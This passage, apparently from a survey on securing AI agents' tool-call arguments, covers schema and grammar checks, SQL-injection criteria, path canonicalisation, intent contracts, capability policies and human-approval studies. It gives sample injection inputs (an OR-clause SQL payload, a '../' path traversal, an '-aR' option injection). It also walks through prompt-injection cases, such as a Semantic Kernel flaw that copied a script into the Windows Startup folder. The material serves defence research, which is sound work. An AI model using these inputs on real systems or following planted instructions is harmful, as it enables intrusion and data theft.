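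Researchers classify the same arguments differently. Ameur and colleagues treat an SQL query as a selector and check its syntax, while Santos-Grueiro treats it as something that can have effects of its own. *SchemaCaps* (2026) lists filters among the harmless arguments. That is reasonable for a search, but when a tool deletes records, the filter determines which ones it deletes.

*SchemaCaps* also offers a definition that can settle many of these disputes. An argument is authority-bearing if its value can do any of the following:

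- change the target of the action
- send data to a destination
- change which user or organisation the action runs as
- change how the action executes, for example by running text as a shell command

By this definition, the deletion filter is authority-bearing. The test depends on what the tool does with the value, so nobody can apply it reliably from the schema alone.

An argument's role can also depend on another argument. In `write_file(path, content)`, text that is harmless in a page of notes may run as instructions at the next build if the path leads to a build configuration. PACT can't express this because it gives each argument a fixed role. Santos-Grueiro treats file contents, code patches and package lists as able to cause effects unless a validator limits what they can do.

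Assigning roles also requires deciding whose description of the tool to trust. *SchemaCaps* takes roles only from a list that the client maintains, never from the server that provides the tool. PACT's automatic rules read the schema, so a malicious provider could disguise a target argument by naming it `note`. An attacker who can alter the contracts does not need to disguise the argument. *The Gate Is Only as Honest as Its Contracts* (2026) examines this danger for a related kind of monitor.

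### Finding sinks that nobody declared

PACT's rules would give no basis for classifying Semantic Kernel's `city` argument as a command, because only the framework's code showed that it reached `eval`. Software can search for such connections by *static analysis*, examining a program without running it.

*TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues) treats a language model's output as tainted and traces it through Python programs. The tool starts with 97 known ways to call a model (sources) and 236 functions that can do damage (sinks), including those that run code, open files, query databases or make network requests. A language model finds further sources by recognising developers' own wrappers around the known calls. It then reviews each path from source to sink and discards those that an attacker can't influence or that already have an adequate check.

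TaintP2X found 27 of 35 known flaws. Liu and colleagues' AgentFuzz runs an agent and searches for prompts that reach dangerous operations. It found seven, partly because it could not set up a working test environment for many of the programs. In 4,772 public repositories, TaintP2X flagged 101 paths in 75 projects, and 74 of the paths led to code or command execution. Its developers reported 40 issues, and maintainers confirmed seven.

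In a separate count, 36 of the 114 cases that TaintP2X flagged were false alarms. Some came from functions that resembled model calls, and others from checks that the analysis missed. TaintP2X also misses connections created at runtime, which are common in agent frameworks.

The analysis in *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (Cui, 2026) traces each dangerous operation back to the tool's arguments and records any checks on the way. Cui compares three tools that all run a shell command. The first passes its argument to the command, the second replaces the argument with a constant, and the third checks the argument against a list of permitted values. A search for dangerous functions gives the same result for all three, although the second tool's argument has no effect.

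Despite the paper's title, the analysis starts from a predefined list of operations. It found 23,866 of them in 67 repositories in under an hour on a laptop, and traced 41% back to a possible source. The rate was 84% for operations that write files but only 11% for calls to external tools. Cui also reproduced 22 behaviours in which an agent could reach a dangerous operation. One was a confirmed vulnerability, another awaits disclosure, and the other 20 did not qualify as vulnerabilities because of protections or limits on use. Most results of such a search therefore need review before they can be called flaws.

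Both tools can show that an innocent-looking argument reaches a function already known to be dangerous, as `city` reached `eval`. They help much less when an argument matters because of its meaning. For example, an email's recipient and body usually reach the same sending function, and tracing the data does not show which of them determines where the message goes.

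## Checking the structure of an argument value

After a contract identifies an argument as a target or a command, the adapter must still decide whether the value is acceptable. A value is *structurally valid* if it has the form that the tool and every program behind it require. Software can check this quickly and predictably without knowing where the value came from, but an attacker can often write a harmful value that is structurally valid.

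### Four checks on one value

Structural validity has four layers, each with its own check:

- The JSON parser accepts any call that is valid JSON. This excludes calls that break off halfway or lack a quotation mark.
- The schema requires the right argument names and types, restricts some arguments to a fixed set of values, and forbids undeclared fields.
- The grammar check parses the value as the receiving program would, for example as an email address or a database query.
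- The allowlist check converts the value to its *canonical form*, the one standard form that identifies what the tool would act on, and compares that with a list of what the developer permits.

The ban on undeclared fields is easy to overlook. Without it, the model could add a `bcc` field to `send_email`. If the adapter forwards every field to a mail library that supports blind copies, a stranger would receive a copy even though the recipient is correct.

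To compare the checks, suppose an agent can also write files and run database queries. The user wants it to email the manager, save the summary as `reports/parcels.txt` and look up the total of order 1042. The developer permits recipients at company.com, files under `/work/reports`, and queries that only read the `orders` table. The correct values pass all four checks. The values in each row below pass every earlier check.

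| Check that refuses the value | Recipient | Path | Query |
|---|---|---|---|
| JSON parser | `"manager@company.com` | `"reports\parcels.txt"` | `"SELECT total FR` |
| Schema | `["manager@company.com"]` | `7` | `null` |
| Grammar | `"manager at company"` | A path containing a null character | `"SELECT total FORM orders"` |
| Allowlist | `"stranger@example.net"` | `"reports/../payroll/may.csv"` | `"SELECT email FROM customers"` |
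| None | `"legal-team@company.com"` | `"reports/april.txt"` | `"SELECT total FROM orders WHERE id = 1043"` |

The path in the first row fails because a backslash in a JSON string starts an escape sequence, and `\p` isn't a valid one. The grammar check rejects very few paths, since Linux accepts almost any string without a null character. In the allowlist row, the two dots move up one directory, so the canonical path is `/work/payroll/may.csv`.

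The stranger's address, the payroll file and the customer list are well formed, and only the allowlist blocks them. The values in the last row pass every check, but using them would send the summary to the wrong department, overwrite last month's report and reveal another customer's order.

### What strict schemas guarantee

Model providers can enforce the JSON and schema checks while the model is still writing. *Constrained decoding* compiles the schema into a grammar and, at every step, blocks tokens that would make the output invalid. In Anthropic's *Strict tool use*, the developer adds `strict: true` to a tool's definition, which guarantees a valid tool name and arguments that match the schema. Without this setting, a booking tool that needs a whole number of passengers might receive "2" or "two" instead of 2.

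OpenAI has the same setting and makes the same promise, provided the schema uses only the parts of JSON Schema that OpenAI supports. Its older JSON mode made valid JSON more likely but, according to *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API*, did not guarantee that the output would match a particular schema.

The guarantee has exceptions. Anthropic's *Structured outputs* lists three cases in which the output may not match the schema:

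- The model refuses the request for safety reasons.
- The output reaches its maximum length and stops early.
- The model picks a value from a fixed list but capitalises it differently.

An adapter can detect a refusal or a cut-off output from its stop reason. A listed value with different capitalisation produces no error, so Anthropic advises developers to ignore case when comparing listed values and to avoid lists in which two values differ only in case. Fine-grained streaming delivers arguments faster by sending them as the model writes them, but it also removes a safeguard, and AWS's *Anthropic Claude tool use* tells developers to expect invalid or partial JSON.

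Strict schemas also cannot express every rule. Anthropic does not support minimum and maximum numbers or limits on string length, so its flight-booking example lists the permitted numbers of passengers from 1 to 10 instead. Listing every permitted payment amount would be impractical, so the adapter has to check the amount. A request can include at most 20 strict tools and 24 optional arguments across all its strict schemas. An agent with AgentDojo's 74 tools would have to leave most of them without strict mode or split them across several requests.

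Anthropic supports a format for email addresses, but the stranger's address fits it too. It also supports simple search patterns, so a developer could put part of the allowlist in the schema by requiring every recipient to end in `@company.com`. But constrained decoding would only block the tokens that spell the stranger's address, and the model would continue with the most likely remaining tokens. An agent that had accepted a planted instruction might then email the wrong colleague or an address that doesn't exist. A check at the adapter can stop the call and record the attempt.

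### Keeping an argument within one syntactic unit

Adapters and tools often insert an argument into a longer text, such as a query, that another program parses. Checking the argument alone may miss an attack, because the argument can change how the program parses the surrounding text. Su and Wassermann (2006), in *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications*, gave the first formal definition of this kind of attack. They require each input to stay within one syntactic unit of the finished text.

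Suppose the adapter has a fixed query and inserts only the order number:

```
SELECT total FROM orders WHERE id = «order number»
```

Here are two inputs and the conditions they produce. The angled marks show where the input begins and ends, and the brackets show how the database groups the text into comparisons:

```
( id = «1042» )
( id = «1042 ) OR ( id = 1043» )
```

The first input is exactly one number. The second starts inside one comparison and ends inside another, so no part of the parse tree matches it exactly, which means it has changed the structure of the query.

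For the exact definition, let `U` be the set of units that the developer permits, such as numbers, strings and names. A query `q` with parse tree `T` is an injection if both of these hold:

```
1. q is valid SQL
2. some input in q is not the complete text of a node in T
   whose type belongs to U
```

The first condition excludes queries that would fail to run. The set `U` makes the rule adjustable, which some applications need. The bug tracker Bugzilla, for example, stores search conditions, so it has to accept a whole condition as input.

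The criterion catches attacks that escaping misses. In Su and Wassermann's main example, an online store escapes every quotation mark in its customers' input. But the query compares the credit card type with an unquoted number, so an attacker can add a condition without typing a quotation mark and retrieve every card number in the database.

Su and Wassermann enforced their rule with a program called SQLCheck. It marks the beginning and end of each input, and the application then builds the query with the marks in place. SQLCheck parses the result with a modified grammar, in which a marked passage must be exactly one permitted unit. If the query parses, SQLCheck removes the marks and sends the query to the database. Su and Wassermann proved that this procedure accepts a query if and only if it is valid and not an injection by their definition.

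Su and Wassermann tested SQLCheck on five web applications, each with a PHP and a JSP version. For each language, it blocked all 18,424 attacks and allowed all 3,824 legitimate queries, taking about 3 milliseconds per query. The attacks came from published reports of real vulnerabilities and were not designed to defeat SQLCheck. An attacker who discovered the marks, which were random four-letter strings, could have forged them. They proposed escaping any marks that appear in the input.

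The criterion works just as well when a model writes the input, as long as a developer wrote the rest of the text. It would have stopped the attack on the hotel agent's `city` argument (CVE-2026-26030) and would also reject a `city` value that added an otherwise permitted comparison to the filter.

This definition stops being useful when the model writes the whole query, because it assumes that the fixed parts of a query express the programmer's intentions, and here there are no fixed parts. The query is a single unit, a complete statement, so the developer can only permit every valid query or forbid them all.

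We might try to mark only the passages that came from a web page. But SQLCheck needs every function `f` that processes an input `x` to keep the marks around the result:

```
f(«x») = «f(x)»
```

Ordinary functions that trim or escape text can preserve the marks in their input. A language model that reads a marked page and then writes a query is not guaranteed to preserve them, for the same reason that taint marks do not survive a model call.

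For queries the model writes, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend a read-only database account, an allowlist of parts of the database, and a check of the query's syntax tree that rejects destructive operations. A narrower tool would often be better. If the agent only needs order totals, the developer can write the query and let the model supply the order number. The model could still supply 1043, which satisfies the criterion because it is a single number.

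### Values that no parser reads as code

The easiest way to keep a value within one unit is to send it separately. Parameterised queries do this with a placeholder where the value belongs:

```python
db.execute("SELECT total FROM orders WHERE id = ?", [order_id])
```

The database parses the query with the placeholder in it and treats the contents of `order_id` as a single value. Even if the text contains OR, it can't add a second condition. Placeholders can stand only for values, so if the model also chooses which table to search, the adapter should pick the table's name from a fixed list.

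A similar solution works for commands. A *shell* is a program that splits a line of text into a command and its arguments and gives characters such as spaces and semicolons a special meaning. The adapter can avoid the shell by giving the operating system a list with the program's name and each argument as separate items, so a semicolon in a file name is an ordinary character.

The program that receives the list may still misread an item, because many programs treat anything starting with a hyphen as an option. MITRE's *CWE-88*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, calls this argument injection and gives a harmless example in which a program runs `ls -l` to show the details of one file. The program accepts only names made of letters, digits, underscores and hyphens. The name `-aR` passes that check, but `ls` reads it as two options and lists the whole directory, including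 hidden files and all subdirectories.

An argument list does not prevent this, since `-aR` is already a single item. The usual remedy is a separator of two hyphens, after which `ls` treats everything as a file name:

```python
subprocess.run(["ls", "-l", name])         # "-aR" acts as two options
subprocess.run(["ls", "-l", "--", name])   # "-aR" is a file name
```

Not every program supports the separator. MITRE also suggests requiring a letter or digit at the start of the name, or listing the files with the programming language's own functions instead of running a command. More generally, approving a command by name leaves its options unchecked, and an option can completely change what the command does.

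A grammar check can also fail because it uses the wrong grammar. MITRE describes a flaw in PHPMailer, a library for sending email. The library checked that the sender's address was well formed, but not that it was safe in the command it was added to. The rules for email addresses are loose and allow spaces in some places, so an attacker could write a valid address that the mail program interpreted as an address followed by extra options, including one that named a program to run.

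### A file path that escaped the sandbox

Paths, for example, need the allowlist check because almost any string is a valid path. Microsoft describes a serious case in its account of CVE-2026-25592, the Semantic Kernel flaw that exposed a file-transfer function to the model.

Semantic Kernel has a plugin that runs an agent's Python code in a *sandbox*, an isolated environment in Microsoft's cloud with its own file system. The agent runs on another computer, the host, where helper functions copy files into and out of the sandbox. The exposed function, `DownloadFileAsync`, copies files out in the .NET version of the framework. The framework did not check the function's `localFilePath` argument, which specifies the file's destination on the host.

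A planted instruction could get code out of the sandbox with two ordinary tool calls. The first created a script inside the sandbox, where it could not harm the host. The second copied the script into the host's Startup folder, so Windows ran it on the host the next time the user signed in. The destination path was a string, as the schema required, and a valid Windows path, so neither a schema check nor a grammar check would have stopped the copy.

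Version 1.71.0 fixed the flaw in two ways. The developers removed the line that offered the function to the model, which is the stronger protection because the model can no longer call the function. For applications that call the function from their own code, they added a check that converts the path to a full, canonical path and tests whether it lies in a permitted directory. This check still matters if a developer's code passes the function a path that the model suggested.

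In both the Python and .NET versions, the function that copies files into the sandbox accepted any path on the host, so a planted instruction could make the agent copy a private SSH key into the sandbox. Microsoft describes the new upload protections as opt-in.

MITRE recommends decoding and canonicalising a value before validating it, because later decoding can bring back characters that the check was meant to exclude. Decoding the value twice can also bring them back. If the adapter joins a directory to a file name, it should check the combined path, which can be unacceptable even when each part is acceptable.

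The adapter also has to compare whole directory names, because the path `/work/reports-old/may.txt` begins with the characters `/work/reports` but is in a different directory. A path inside a permitted directory can also be a symbolic link, a file that redirects to another location. The .NET function that Semantic Kernel uses, `Path.GetFullPath`, resolves `..` but does not follow symbolic links. If outsiders can create links in a directory where the agent works, the adapter should resolve them before it compares the path.

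### Well-formed values with the wrong meaning

Some values have the right type but are still unusable. *Gecko* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool that looks up share prices and expects a stock symbol such as AAPL. If the model writes "Apple Inc." instead, the value is a string, as the schema requires, but the tool can't look it up.

Gecko is a simulated environment where an agent can try tool calls before making real ones. Ordinary code first checks each call against the rules in the schema, such as required arguments, types, number ranges and permitted values. A helper language model then compares the arguments with the tool's description and looks for *semantic errors*, which are values that have the right form but the wrong meaning.

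Zhang and colleagues tested the checks on a set of single tool calls with three different helper models:

| Helper model | Correct arguments accepted | Syntactic errors caught | Semantic errors caught |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 100% | 100% | 71% |
| GPT-4.1 nano | 100% | 100% | 69% |
| Qwen2.5 7B | 100% | 100% | 63% |

The rules caught every error that a schema can describe, so a model isn't needed for those checks. The helper missed roughly a third of the remaining errors, and changing its model made only a modest difference. It may have missed some of these errors because it is prompted to accept an argument whenever it is uncertain. That helps avoid false alarms in a simulation, but a security check on a sink argument should reject the argument when uncertain.

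Developers can catch some semantic errors by comparing a value with a list of allowed values. In MITRE's example, the word "boat" in a field for colours passes a test for letters but fails a comparison with a list of colours. An adapter could similarly compare a stock symbol with the exchange's list.

Gecko's figures measure how well it catches mistakes, not attacks. An attacker's value need not contain a mistake, and the attacker can write text meant to influence the helper's output. The stranger's address is correctly formatted and fits any reasonable description of a recipient. The helper could flag it only by comparing it with the user's request, and the paper is unclear about whether the helper receives that request. The main text lists the user's task among the helper's inputs, but the appendix lists only the tool call and the schema.

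## Whether the user authorised the value

Comparing an argument with the user's request can catch mistakes that involve no attacker. For example, a user asks the model to send a summary to "my manager", and the model sends it to legal-team@company.com, an address it picked from the company directory. The source is trusted and the address is well formed, so checks of origin and structure would not stop the email. Ameur and colleagues call such a value *trusted but unauthorised*. It can come from an outdated directory, an old email thread or a document that an insider planted, and the summary reaches the wrong people, as it would after an injection.

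Origin, structure and authorisation are separate properties, as a few recipients show:

| Recipient | Trusted origin | Valid address | Authorised by the user |
|---|---|---|---|
| manager@company.com, from the request | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| legal-team@company.com, from the directory | Yes | Yes | No |
| Dora's address, from her website | No | Yes | Yes |
| stranger@example.net, from the customs page | No | Yes | No |
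| "manager at company", typed by the user | Yes | No | Yes |

A user can authorise a value by writing it out, by describing it ("my manager") or by saying where to find it ("the address on her website"). Software can find a written value by matching text, but a description needs interpretation, and a value the agent has to look up isn't in the request.

### The intent contract

IntentFlow, which Ameur and colleagues released in November 2026, checks each call against an *intent contract*, a record of what the user authorised. A language model writes the contract from the request. It lists the action, the expected values (such as a recipient, path, date or query) and the arguments that need protection. For the email to the manager it might look like this:

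```json
{
  "action": "send_email",
  "expected": {"recipient": "manager@company.com"},
  "protected": ["recipient", "attachment"]
}
```

The user wrote only "my manager", so the address comes from an *alias directory*, a table that links phrases to values. The prototype's table has 15 entries and 77 phrases. An *endpoint registry* does the same for endpoints, the network addresses of services that receive the agent's queries. It also follows redirects and detects lookalike characters in domain names. People maintain both tables by hand.

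For each argument of a proposed call, IntentFlow takes these steps:

1. It looks up the argument's role.
2. It converts the value to a standard form and searches the request and the retrieved documents for its source.
3. It compares the value with the contract and with the text of the request.
4. It checks whether an argument with this role may take a value from that source.

A sink argument is safe only if it passes both comparisons:

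```
safe(v) = the user's intent authorises v for this argument
          and v's source is allowed for the argument's role
```

Each argument gets one of four outcomes: Allow, Sanitise (rewrite the value, then run the call), Confirm (ask the user) or Block. The strictest outcome among the arguments applies to the whole call. IntentFlow's strict mode blocks the email to legal-team@company.com because the contract specifies a different address, even though the directory is an acceptable source. AuthGraph, which checks whether a value came from the expected tool, would accept the address if it treated the directory as a proper source of recipients.

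This design depends on the alias directory being correct. If its entry for "my manager" still lists last year's manager, IntentFlow will authorise the wrong address. The comparison with the request is also crude. Except for endpoints, the prototype accepts any string that appears in the request, including a fragment such as ager@company.com.

### What intent adds to provenance

Ameur and colleagues tested IntentFlow on synthetic tasks with four tools for sending email, creating calendar events, writing files and running database queries. The main test had 200 attacks, and a second had 50 trusted but unauthorised values and 50 legitimate tasks.

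| Check | Main attacks that ran, of 200 | Trusted-but-unauthorised values that ran, of 50 | Legitimate tasks allowed in the second test, of 50 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Provenance alone | 101 | 50 | 50 |
| Intent alone | 74 | 2 | 50 |
| CaMeL-style | 74 | 0 | 34 |
| IntentFlow, strict | 24 | 0 | 50 |

In the main test, the attack success rate was 50.5% with provenance alone and 12.0% with IntentFlow. All 24 attacks that got past IntentFlow changed an email's subject, an event's description or a file's contents. None of the 134 attacks on recipients, attachments, participants, paths or endpoints succeeded. The 12.0% rate therefore depends mainly on how many attacks on subjects, descriptions and file contents the researchers included.

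Intent checks stopped most of the attacks, and checks on the syntax of database queries stopped 34 more. Provenance checks stopped at most another 16. But the contracts in this test were not generated by a model, and Ameur and colleagues point out that provenance could matter more if a model generated them and made errors.

In the second test, checking provenance alone caught none of the wrong values because every one came from a trusted internal document. Checking intent alone let two through because the contracts supplied for those tasks mistakenly listed the attacker's endpoint. A simplified stand-in for CaMeL, which accepts a value only if the request contains it word for word, blocked all 50 wrong values. It also blocked 16 legitimate tasks because the request described a person (3 tasks) or an endpoint (13 tasks) instead of giving the exact value. Because the check is simplified, these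 results are only weak evidence of how CaMeL itself would perform.

IntentFlow also had trouble with endpoints. In a separate test, strict mode blocked all 30 attacks but allowed only 14 of 30 legitimate requests, because it rejects any endpoint it cannot resolve. A looser version that accepted unresolved endpoints did not increase the number of legitimate requests allowed, and five attacks succeeded.

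These results depend on information that a deployed system would not have. Ameur and colleagues supplied the contract for each task, and in the main test they also gave IntentFlow labels showing which documents contained injections. When GPT-4o mini wrote the contracts instead, none of the 400 decisions in the main test changed, but Ameur and colleagues say this benchmark barely tests contract writing. They also declared every argument's role by hand. If their automatic method assigned the roles instead, any sink argument it missed would skip the strict check, and it missed 25.9% of sink arguments on other tools. They have not yet run the system with both contracts and roles inferred.

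In a smaller experiment, a live model wrote the calls, and the researchers again supplied the contracts and injection labels. GPT-4o mini wrote a corrupted call in 17 of 110 attacked tasks, and IntentFlow stopped all 17.

### Values from earlier tasks

A system can also learn which values are normal from the agent's completed tasks. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues, 2026) describes a defence that records each combination of tool, argument and value from attack-free runs in an allowlist. The allowlist covers arguments whose values change slowly, such as recipients, account numbers and file references. It leaves out message bodies and web addresses, which are usually new each time.

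A familiar value can still be wrong for the current task. In one of the paper's examples, some users want to email lily.white@gmail.com. Another user only wants to delete a calendar event, but a planted instruction tells the agent to email Lily. A single allowlist for all these tasks would either let the attack through or block the legitimate emails.

Agent-Sentry therefore accepts a listed value only if it also came from a trusted source. This check is the second of three layers. The first is a classifier that examines the sequence of calls and the sources of their arguments. If neither layer can decide whether to allow a call, a language model compares the call with the user's request. In the example, the language model blocks the email because the user never asked to email anyone.

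When Agent-Sentry used a trained classifier, the allowlist settled only 0.8% of decisions, the classifier 96.1%, and the language model the remaining 3.1%. Its results are therefore better evidence about the classifier than about the allowlist.

Sequeira and colleagues report that Agent-Sentry blocked 94.3% of attacks and allowed 95.1% of legitimate runs on AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a benchmark whose tasks depend more on what the agent finds as it works. These figures come from a version that uses rules instead of the trained classifier, and the researchers tested it on the same runs they used to build its rules and allowlist. When they held some runs back for testing, it blocked 93.2% of attacks and allowed 87.1% of legitimate runs.

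Agent-Sentry might not stop the email to the legal team. The directory is a trusted source, and if anyone had used the agent to email the legal team before, the address would be on the list. The call could then pass without reaching the language model, the only layer that interprets the request.

### Permissions fixed before the agent reads anything

Untrusted text can't influence permissions set before the agent reads it. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) applies this idea to coding agents in a system called CapScope. At the start, a language model receives only the user's request and the project's file names, and predicts which files and commands the task will need. Ordinary code turns the prediction into *capabilities*, each permitting one kind of action (read, write or run) on certain paths or commands. (CaMeL uses the same word for its tags on values.) CapScope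 stores the capabilities outside the model's input, so nothing the agent reads later can add to them.

CapScope also gives each agent its own permissions. In the paper's main example, a developer asks a coordinating agent to fix failing login tests, and it has one sub-agent run the tests and another edit the code. The test output contains a planted instruction to replace a signing key in a source file with the attacker's key. The repair requires editing source files, so a single policy for the whole task would permit this edit. Under CapScope, the sub-agent that reads the instruction can run tests but not write files, so the edit fails.

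Bouras and colleagues tested five small Python repairs, with 75 runs for each kind of policy:

| Policy | Runs in which the planted action took effect | Repairs completed | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 | 72 | 145 s |
| One fixed policy for all tasks | 46 | 70 | 140 s |
| One policy per task, shared by all agents | 33 | 68 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 | 68 | 316 s |

The shared policy was also fixed in advance and tailored to the task, so much of the benefit came from dividing permissions among the agents. CapScope took longer partly because agents kept retrying blocked calls. In two of its seven failed repairs, the initial prediction had left out permission to edit the source code.

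All three successful attacks came through a project file of instructions for agents. Planted text can lead the coordinating agent to request more permissions for a sub-agent than the subtask needs, and CapScope will grant them if they are within the whole task's limits. The permissions are also broader than an intent contract. An agent that may write anywhere in a directory can put any text in any file there, so CapScope would not detect that the agent had picked the wrong file.

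### Values that the agent discovers during the task

Permissions fixed at the start don't work when the request leaves out necessary details. Suppose a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. The agent doesn't learn until it opens the email that it has to summarise recent messages and post the summary to the user's Slack account.

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, handle this example with a policy that can change during the task. The policy consists of rules about tool names and argument values, such as one that allows a Slack message only if the recipient is `alice`, the user's Slack handle. A language model writes the first policy from the request and may propose a new one after a tool returns a result. An SMT solver, a program that decides whether logical conditions can all hold at once, then compares the two policies. If `A(P)` is the set of calls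 that policy `P` allows, then:

```
A(P′) ⊆ A(P)    narrowing: Progent applies P′ automatically
otherwise       expansion: P′ needs approval
```

Adding the Slack tool after reading the to-do list expands the policy. Restricting the tool's recipient to `alice`, once the agent has looked up the handle, narrows it. If a recent email contains an instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger, following it would require adding the email tool to the policy, which is another expansion. Even if the instruction misleads the language model, the new permission doesn't take effect without approval.

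With GPT-4o as the agent on AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without a defence and 1.0% succeeded with Progent. On ASB, another benchmark of attacks on agents, Progent lowered the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. In these experiments, however, the system approved every expansion automatically, so the solver's comparison did not stop any of the attacks. The improvement came from the narrow policies that the language model wrote. The first policy, without later changes, lowered the rate on AgentDojo to 2.5%.

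Sequeira and colleagues found that Progent allowed only 69.2% of legitimate runs on their own benchmark. But they gave each agent one fixed policy instead of writing a new policy for each task, so their result doesn't measure Progent as Shi and colleagues designed it. A policy written for deleting a calendar event wouldn't need to allow email, which would solve the problem with Lily's address.

Progent could still authorise the wrong recipient for the manager's email. If the first policy allowed any recipient and the language model then picked the legal team's address from the directory, the new rule would narrow the policy, so Progent would apply it without confirmation. The solver can prove that a policy became stricter but not that the remaining value is the one the user meant.

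*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) introduces SARA, a system that separates what *induces* an action from what *authorises* it. Suppose a user asks the agent to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice. A search result can supply the report's file name, which the agent needs to carry out the request. If the same result also contains an instruction to send a copy to someone else, that instruction induces a second action, which the user did not authorise.

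SARA records the two kinds of information separately. A language model examines each tool result without seeing the user's request, and notes any action that the text suggests, along with the tool and argument values. Another record contains calls that SARA allowed and that ran successfully. Once SARA has found text that suggests an action, a call with outside effects has to pass three tests:

- The operation and its target must be within what the user requested.
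- Any object that the call depends on must come from an earlier call that served the user's task.
- Each argument must have support from the request or such a call, or be a default that adds no authority.

An attacker might try to get around the last test by making an address appear in several places. If a planted instruction names an address and a later contact search returns it, the address might seem to come from a legitimate search. SARA does not let the search result override the first record, so the address still needs support from the user's request.

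Across two models and two benchmarks, SARA lowered the attack success rate from between 16% and 33% with no defence to between 0.06% and 0.63%. In the absence of an attack, the task completion rate fell by 6 to 12 percentage points with SARA and by 16 to 40 points with CaMeL. Removing SARA's test on individual arguments raised the attack success rate for GPT-4o mini from 0.06% to 2.49% on AgentDojo and from 0.17% to 2.73% on AgentDyn. Some harmful calls evidently fit the user's general goal and were wrong only in an argument, such as the recipient.

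SARA's focus on injected text is a weakness in the manager example. An ordinary directory entry doesn't suggest any action, so it would not trigger the full review, and the email to the legal team would go out unchecked.

### Asking the user

If the request does not settle a value, the system can ask the user. IntentFlow has a mode that asks about many values that strict mode would block. In the endpoint test, this mode allowed 28 of the 30 legitimate requests, compared with 14 in strict mode, and no attack succeeded. But no people took part, and Ameur and colleagues assumed that the user would approve every legitimate call and reject every attack. In the test of trusted-but-unauthorised values, IntentFlow asked about 40 of the 50 wrong values, so its perfect result depended on the assumption that the user would reject all 40.

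Real people make many more mistakes. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, asked 80 volunteers to approve or deny an agent's requests. Each person made 12 decisions, half of them about unsafe requests, and saw one of four kinds of prompt:

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
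| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23 s |
| Also the user's original instructions and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 39 s |
| The same facts, organised around the action's consequences | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33 s |

More information helped, although the difference between the last two prompts could be due to chance. If IntentFlow's users made mistakes as often as the people who saw the exact arguments, they would approve about 17 of the 40 wrong values. This is only a rough estimate because the tasks were different.

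Some of the unsafe requests had the right recipient. In one scenario, the user allows an agent to send an auditor only summary totals, but the agent attaches a file built from the raw invoices. The auditor's address is correct and the file name looks ordinary. A reviewer can see the problem only by connecting the attachment with the earlier steps and the original instruction.

Frequent questions also cause people to gradually stop paying attention to what they approve, which Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls *approval fatigue*. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers were each shown a permission prompt for a clearly dangerous command during a coding session. Only 13.6% rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automated classifier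 blocked 89% of the same commands.

Anthropic published these results to support making that classifier the default in its own product. The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful. Each tester saw only one dangerous command, so the drop from 17% to 5% compares different people and doesn't show how any individual changed.

Figures from ordinary use of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, suggest the same conclusion but are harder to interpret. Users approve 97% of permission prompts, which could be reasonable if nearly all the commands are safe. But they reject 39% of the plans the agent submits for approval, so they do seem to exercise judgement when asked about the whole task.

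People tired of approval prompts may turn them off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of problems with agents and files, and finds that user review contributed to 105. Automatic approval was a factor in 80, and prompts that didn't explain a command's effects in 31. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approval may reflect habit or fatigue instead of growing trust. A system that turned repeated approvals into permanent permission could therefore authorise actions the user never really considered.

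Letting users set rules in advance does not necessarily help. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people without software backgrounds supervised an agent through a simulated day. Seven of the agent's 18 actions went beyond the assigned task, such as buying travel insurance or reading private messages. People who had to decide on every action approved 40.3% of these extra actions.

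Another group first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, which left most decisions for later. People had personally approved 133 of the 148 extra actions that ran in that group.

Not all of these approvals were mistakes. Of the people who decided on every action, 88% let the agent call the airport to confirm a flight, and many of them may have wanted the call once they saw it suggested. An approval can confirm what the user already meant, but it can also give the agent new authority. Yan's figures therefore measure how often people accepted actions outside the task, not how often they were careless.

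Asking for approval less often should reduce fatigue. In Progent's AgentDojo tests, only 6% of policy updates were expansions that would need approval. Shi and colleagues report that no attack succeeded when a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, but they assumed the reviewer understood the security risks.

The options a confirmation prompt gives the user also matter. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) notes that LangChain lets a person edit a call's arguments as well as approve or reject it. For the email to the manager, the prompt could show the words "my manager" next to legal-team@company.com and let the user correct the address before the email goes out.

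## Placing the check between model and tool

A check on an argument is useless if the call can reach the tool by another route, or if it changes after the check. A reliable check therefore has to meet three requirements:

- Every call that can have an effect passes the check, with no way around it. This property is called *complete mediation*.
- Nothing that the check inspects can alter the check or its policy.
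- The call that runs is the call that the check approved.

The first two come from the *reference monitor*, an idea from 1970s operating-system security. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) lists its classic properties as complete mediation, resistance to tampering, and a verifiable design.

Complete mediation is hard because agents often have several ways to do the same thing. An agent with a guarded `send_email` tool and an unguarded shell can still send mail by running a command-line mail program. *CONTINUITY* (2026) describes a system that allows protected actions only with a signed permit. In a test that deliberately gave the agent a direct route to the action, the action ran even though every permit check on the normal route still worked.

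Developers can also overlook routes that bypass the check. *Governed MCP* (2026), which describes a check in an operating system's kernel, at first reported that all 123 routes from the agent to the system went through the check. A later test found 59 routes, of which 43 went through it, and the author withdrew the claim. One remedy is to make the other routes unusable. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) describes a kernel rule that lets a tool's process make network connections only to the check. The rule applies even if a programmer forgets a route, but it doesn't stop the tool from changing local files.

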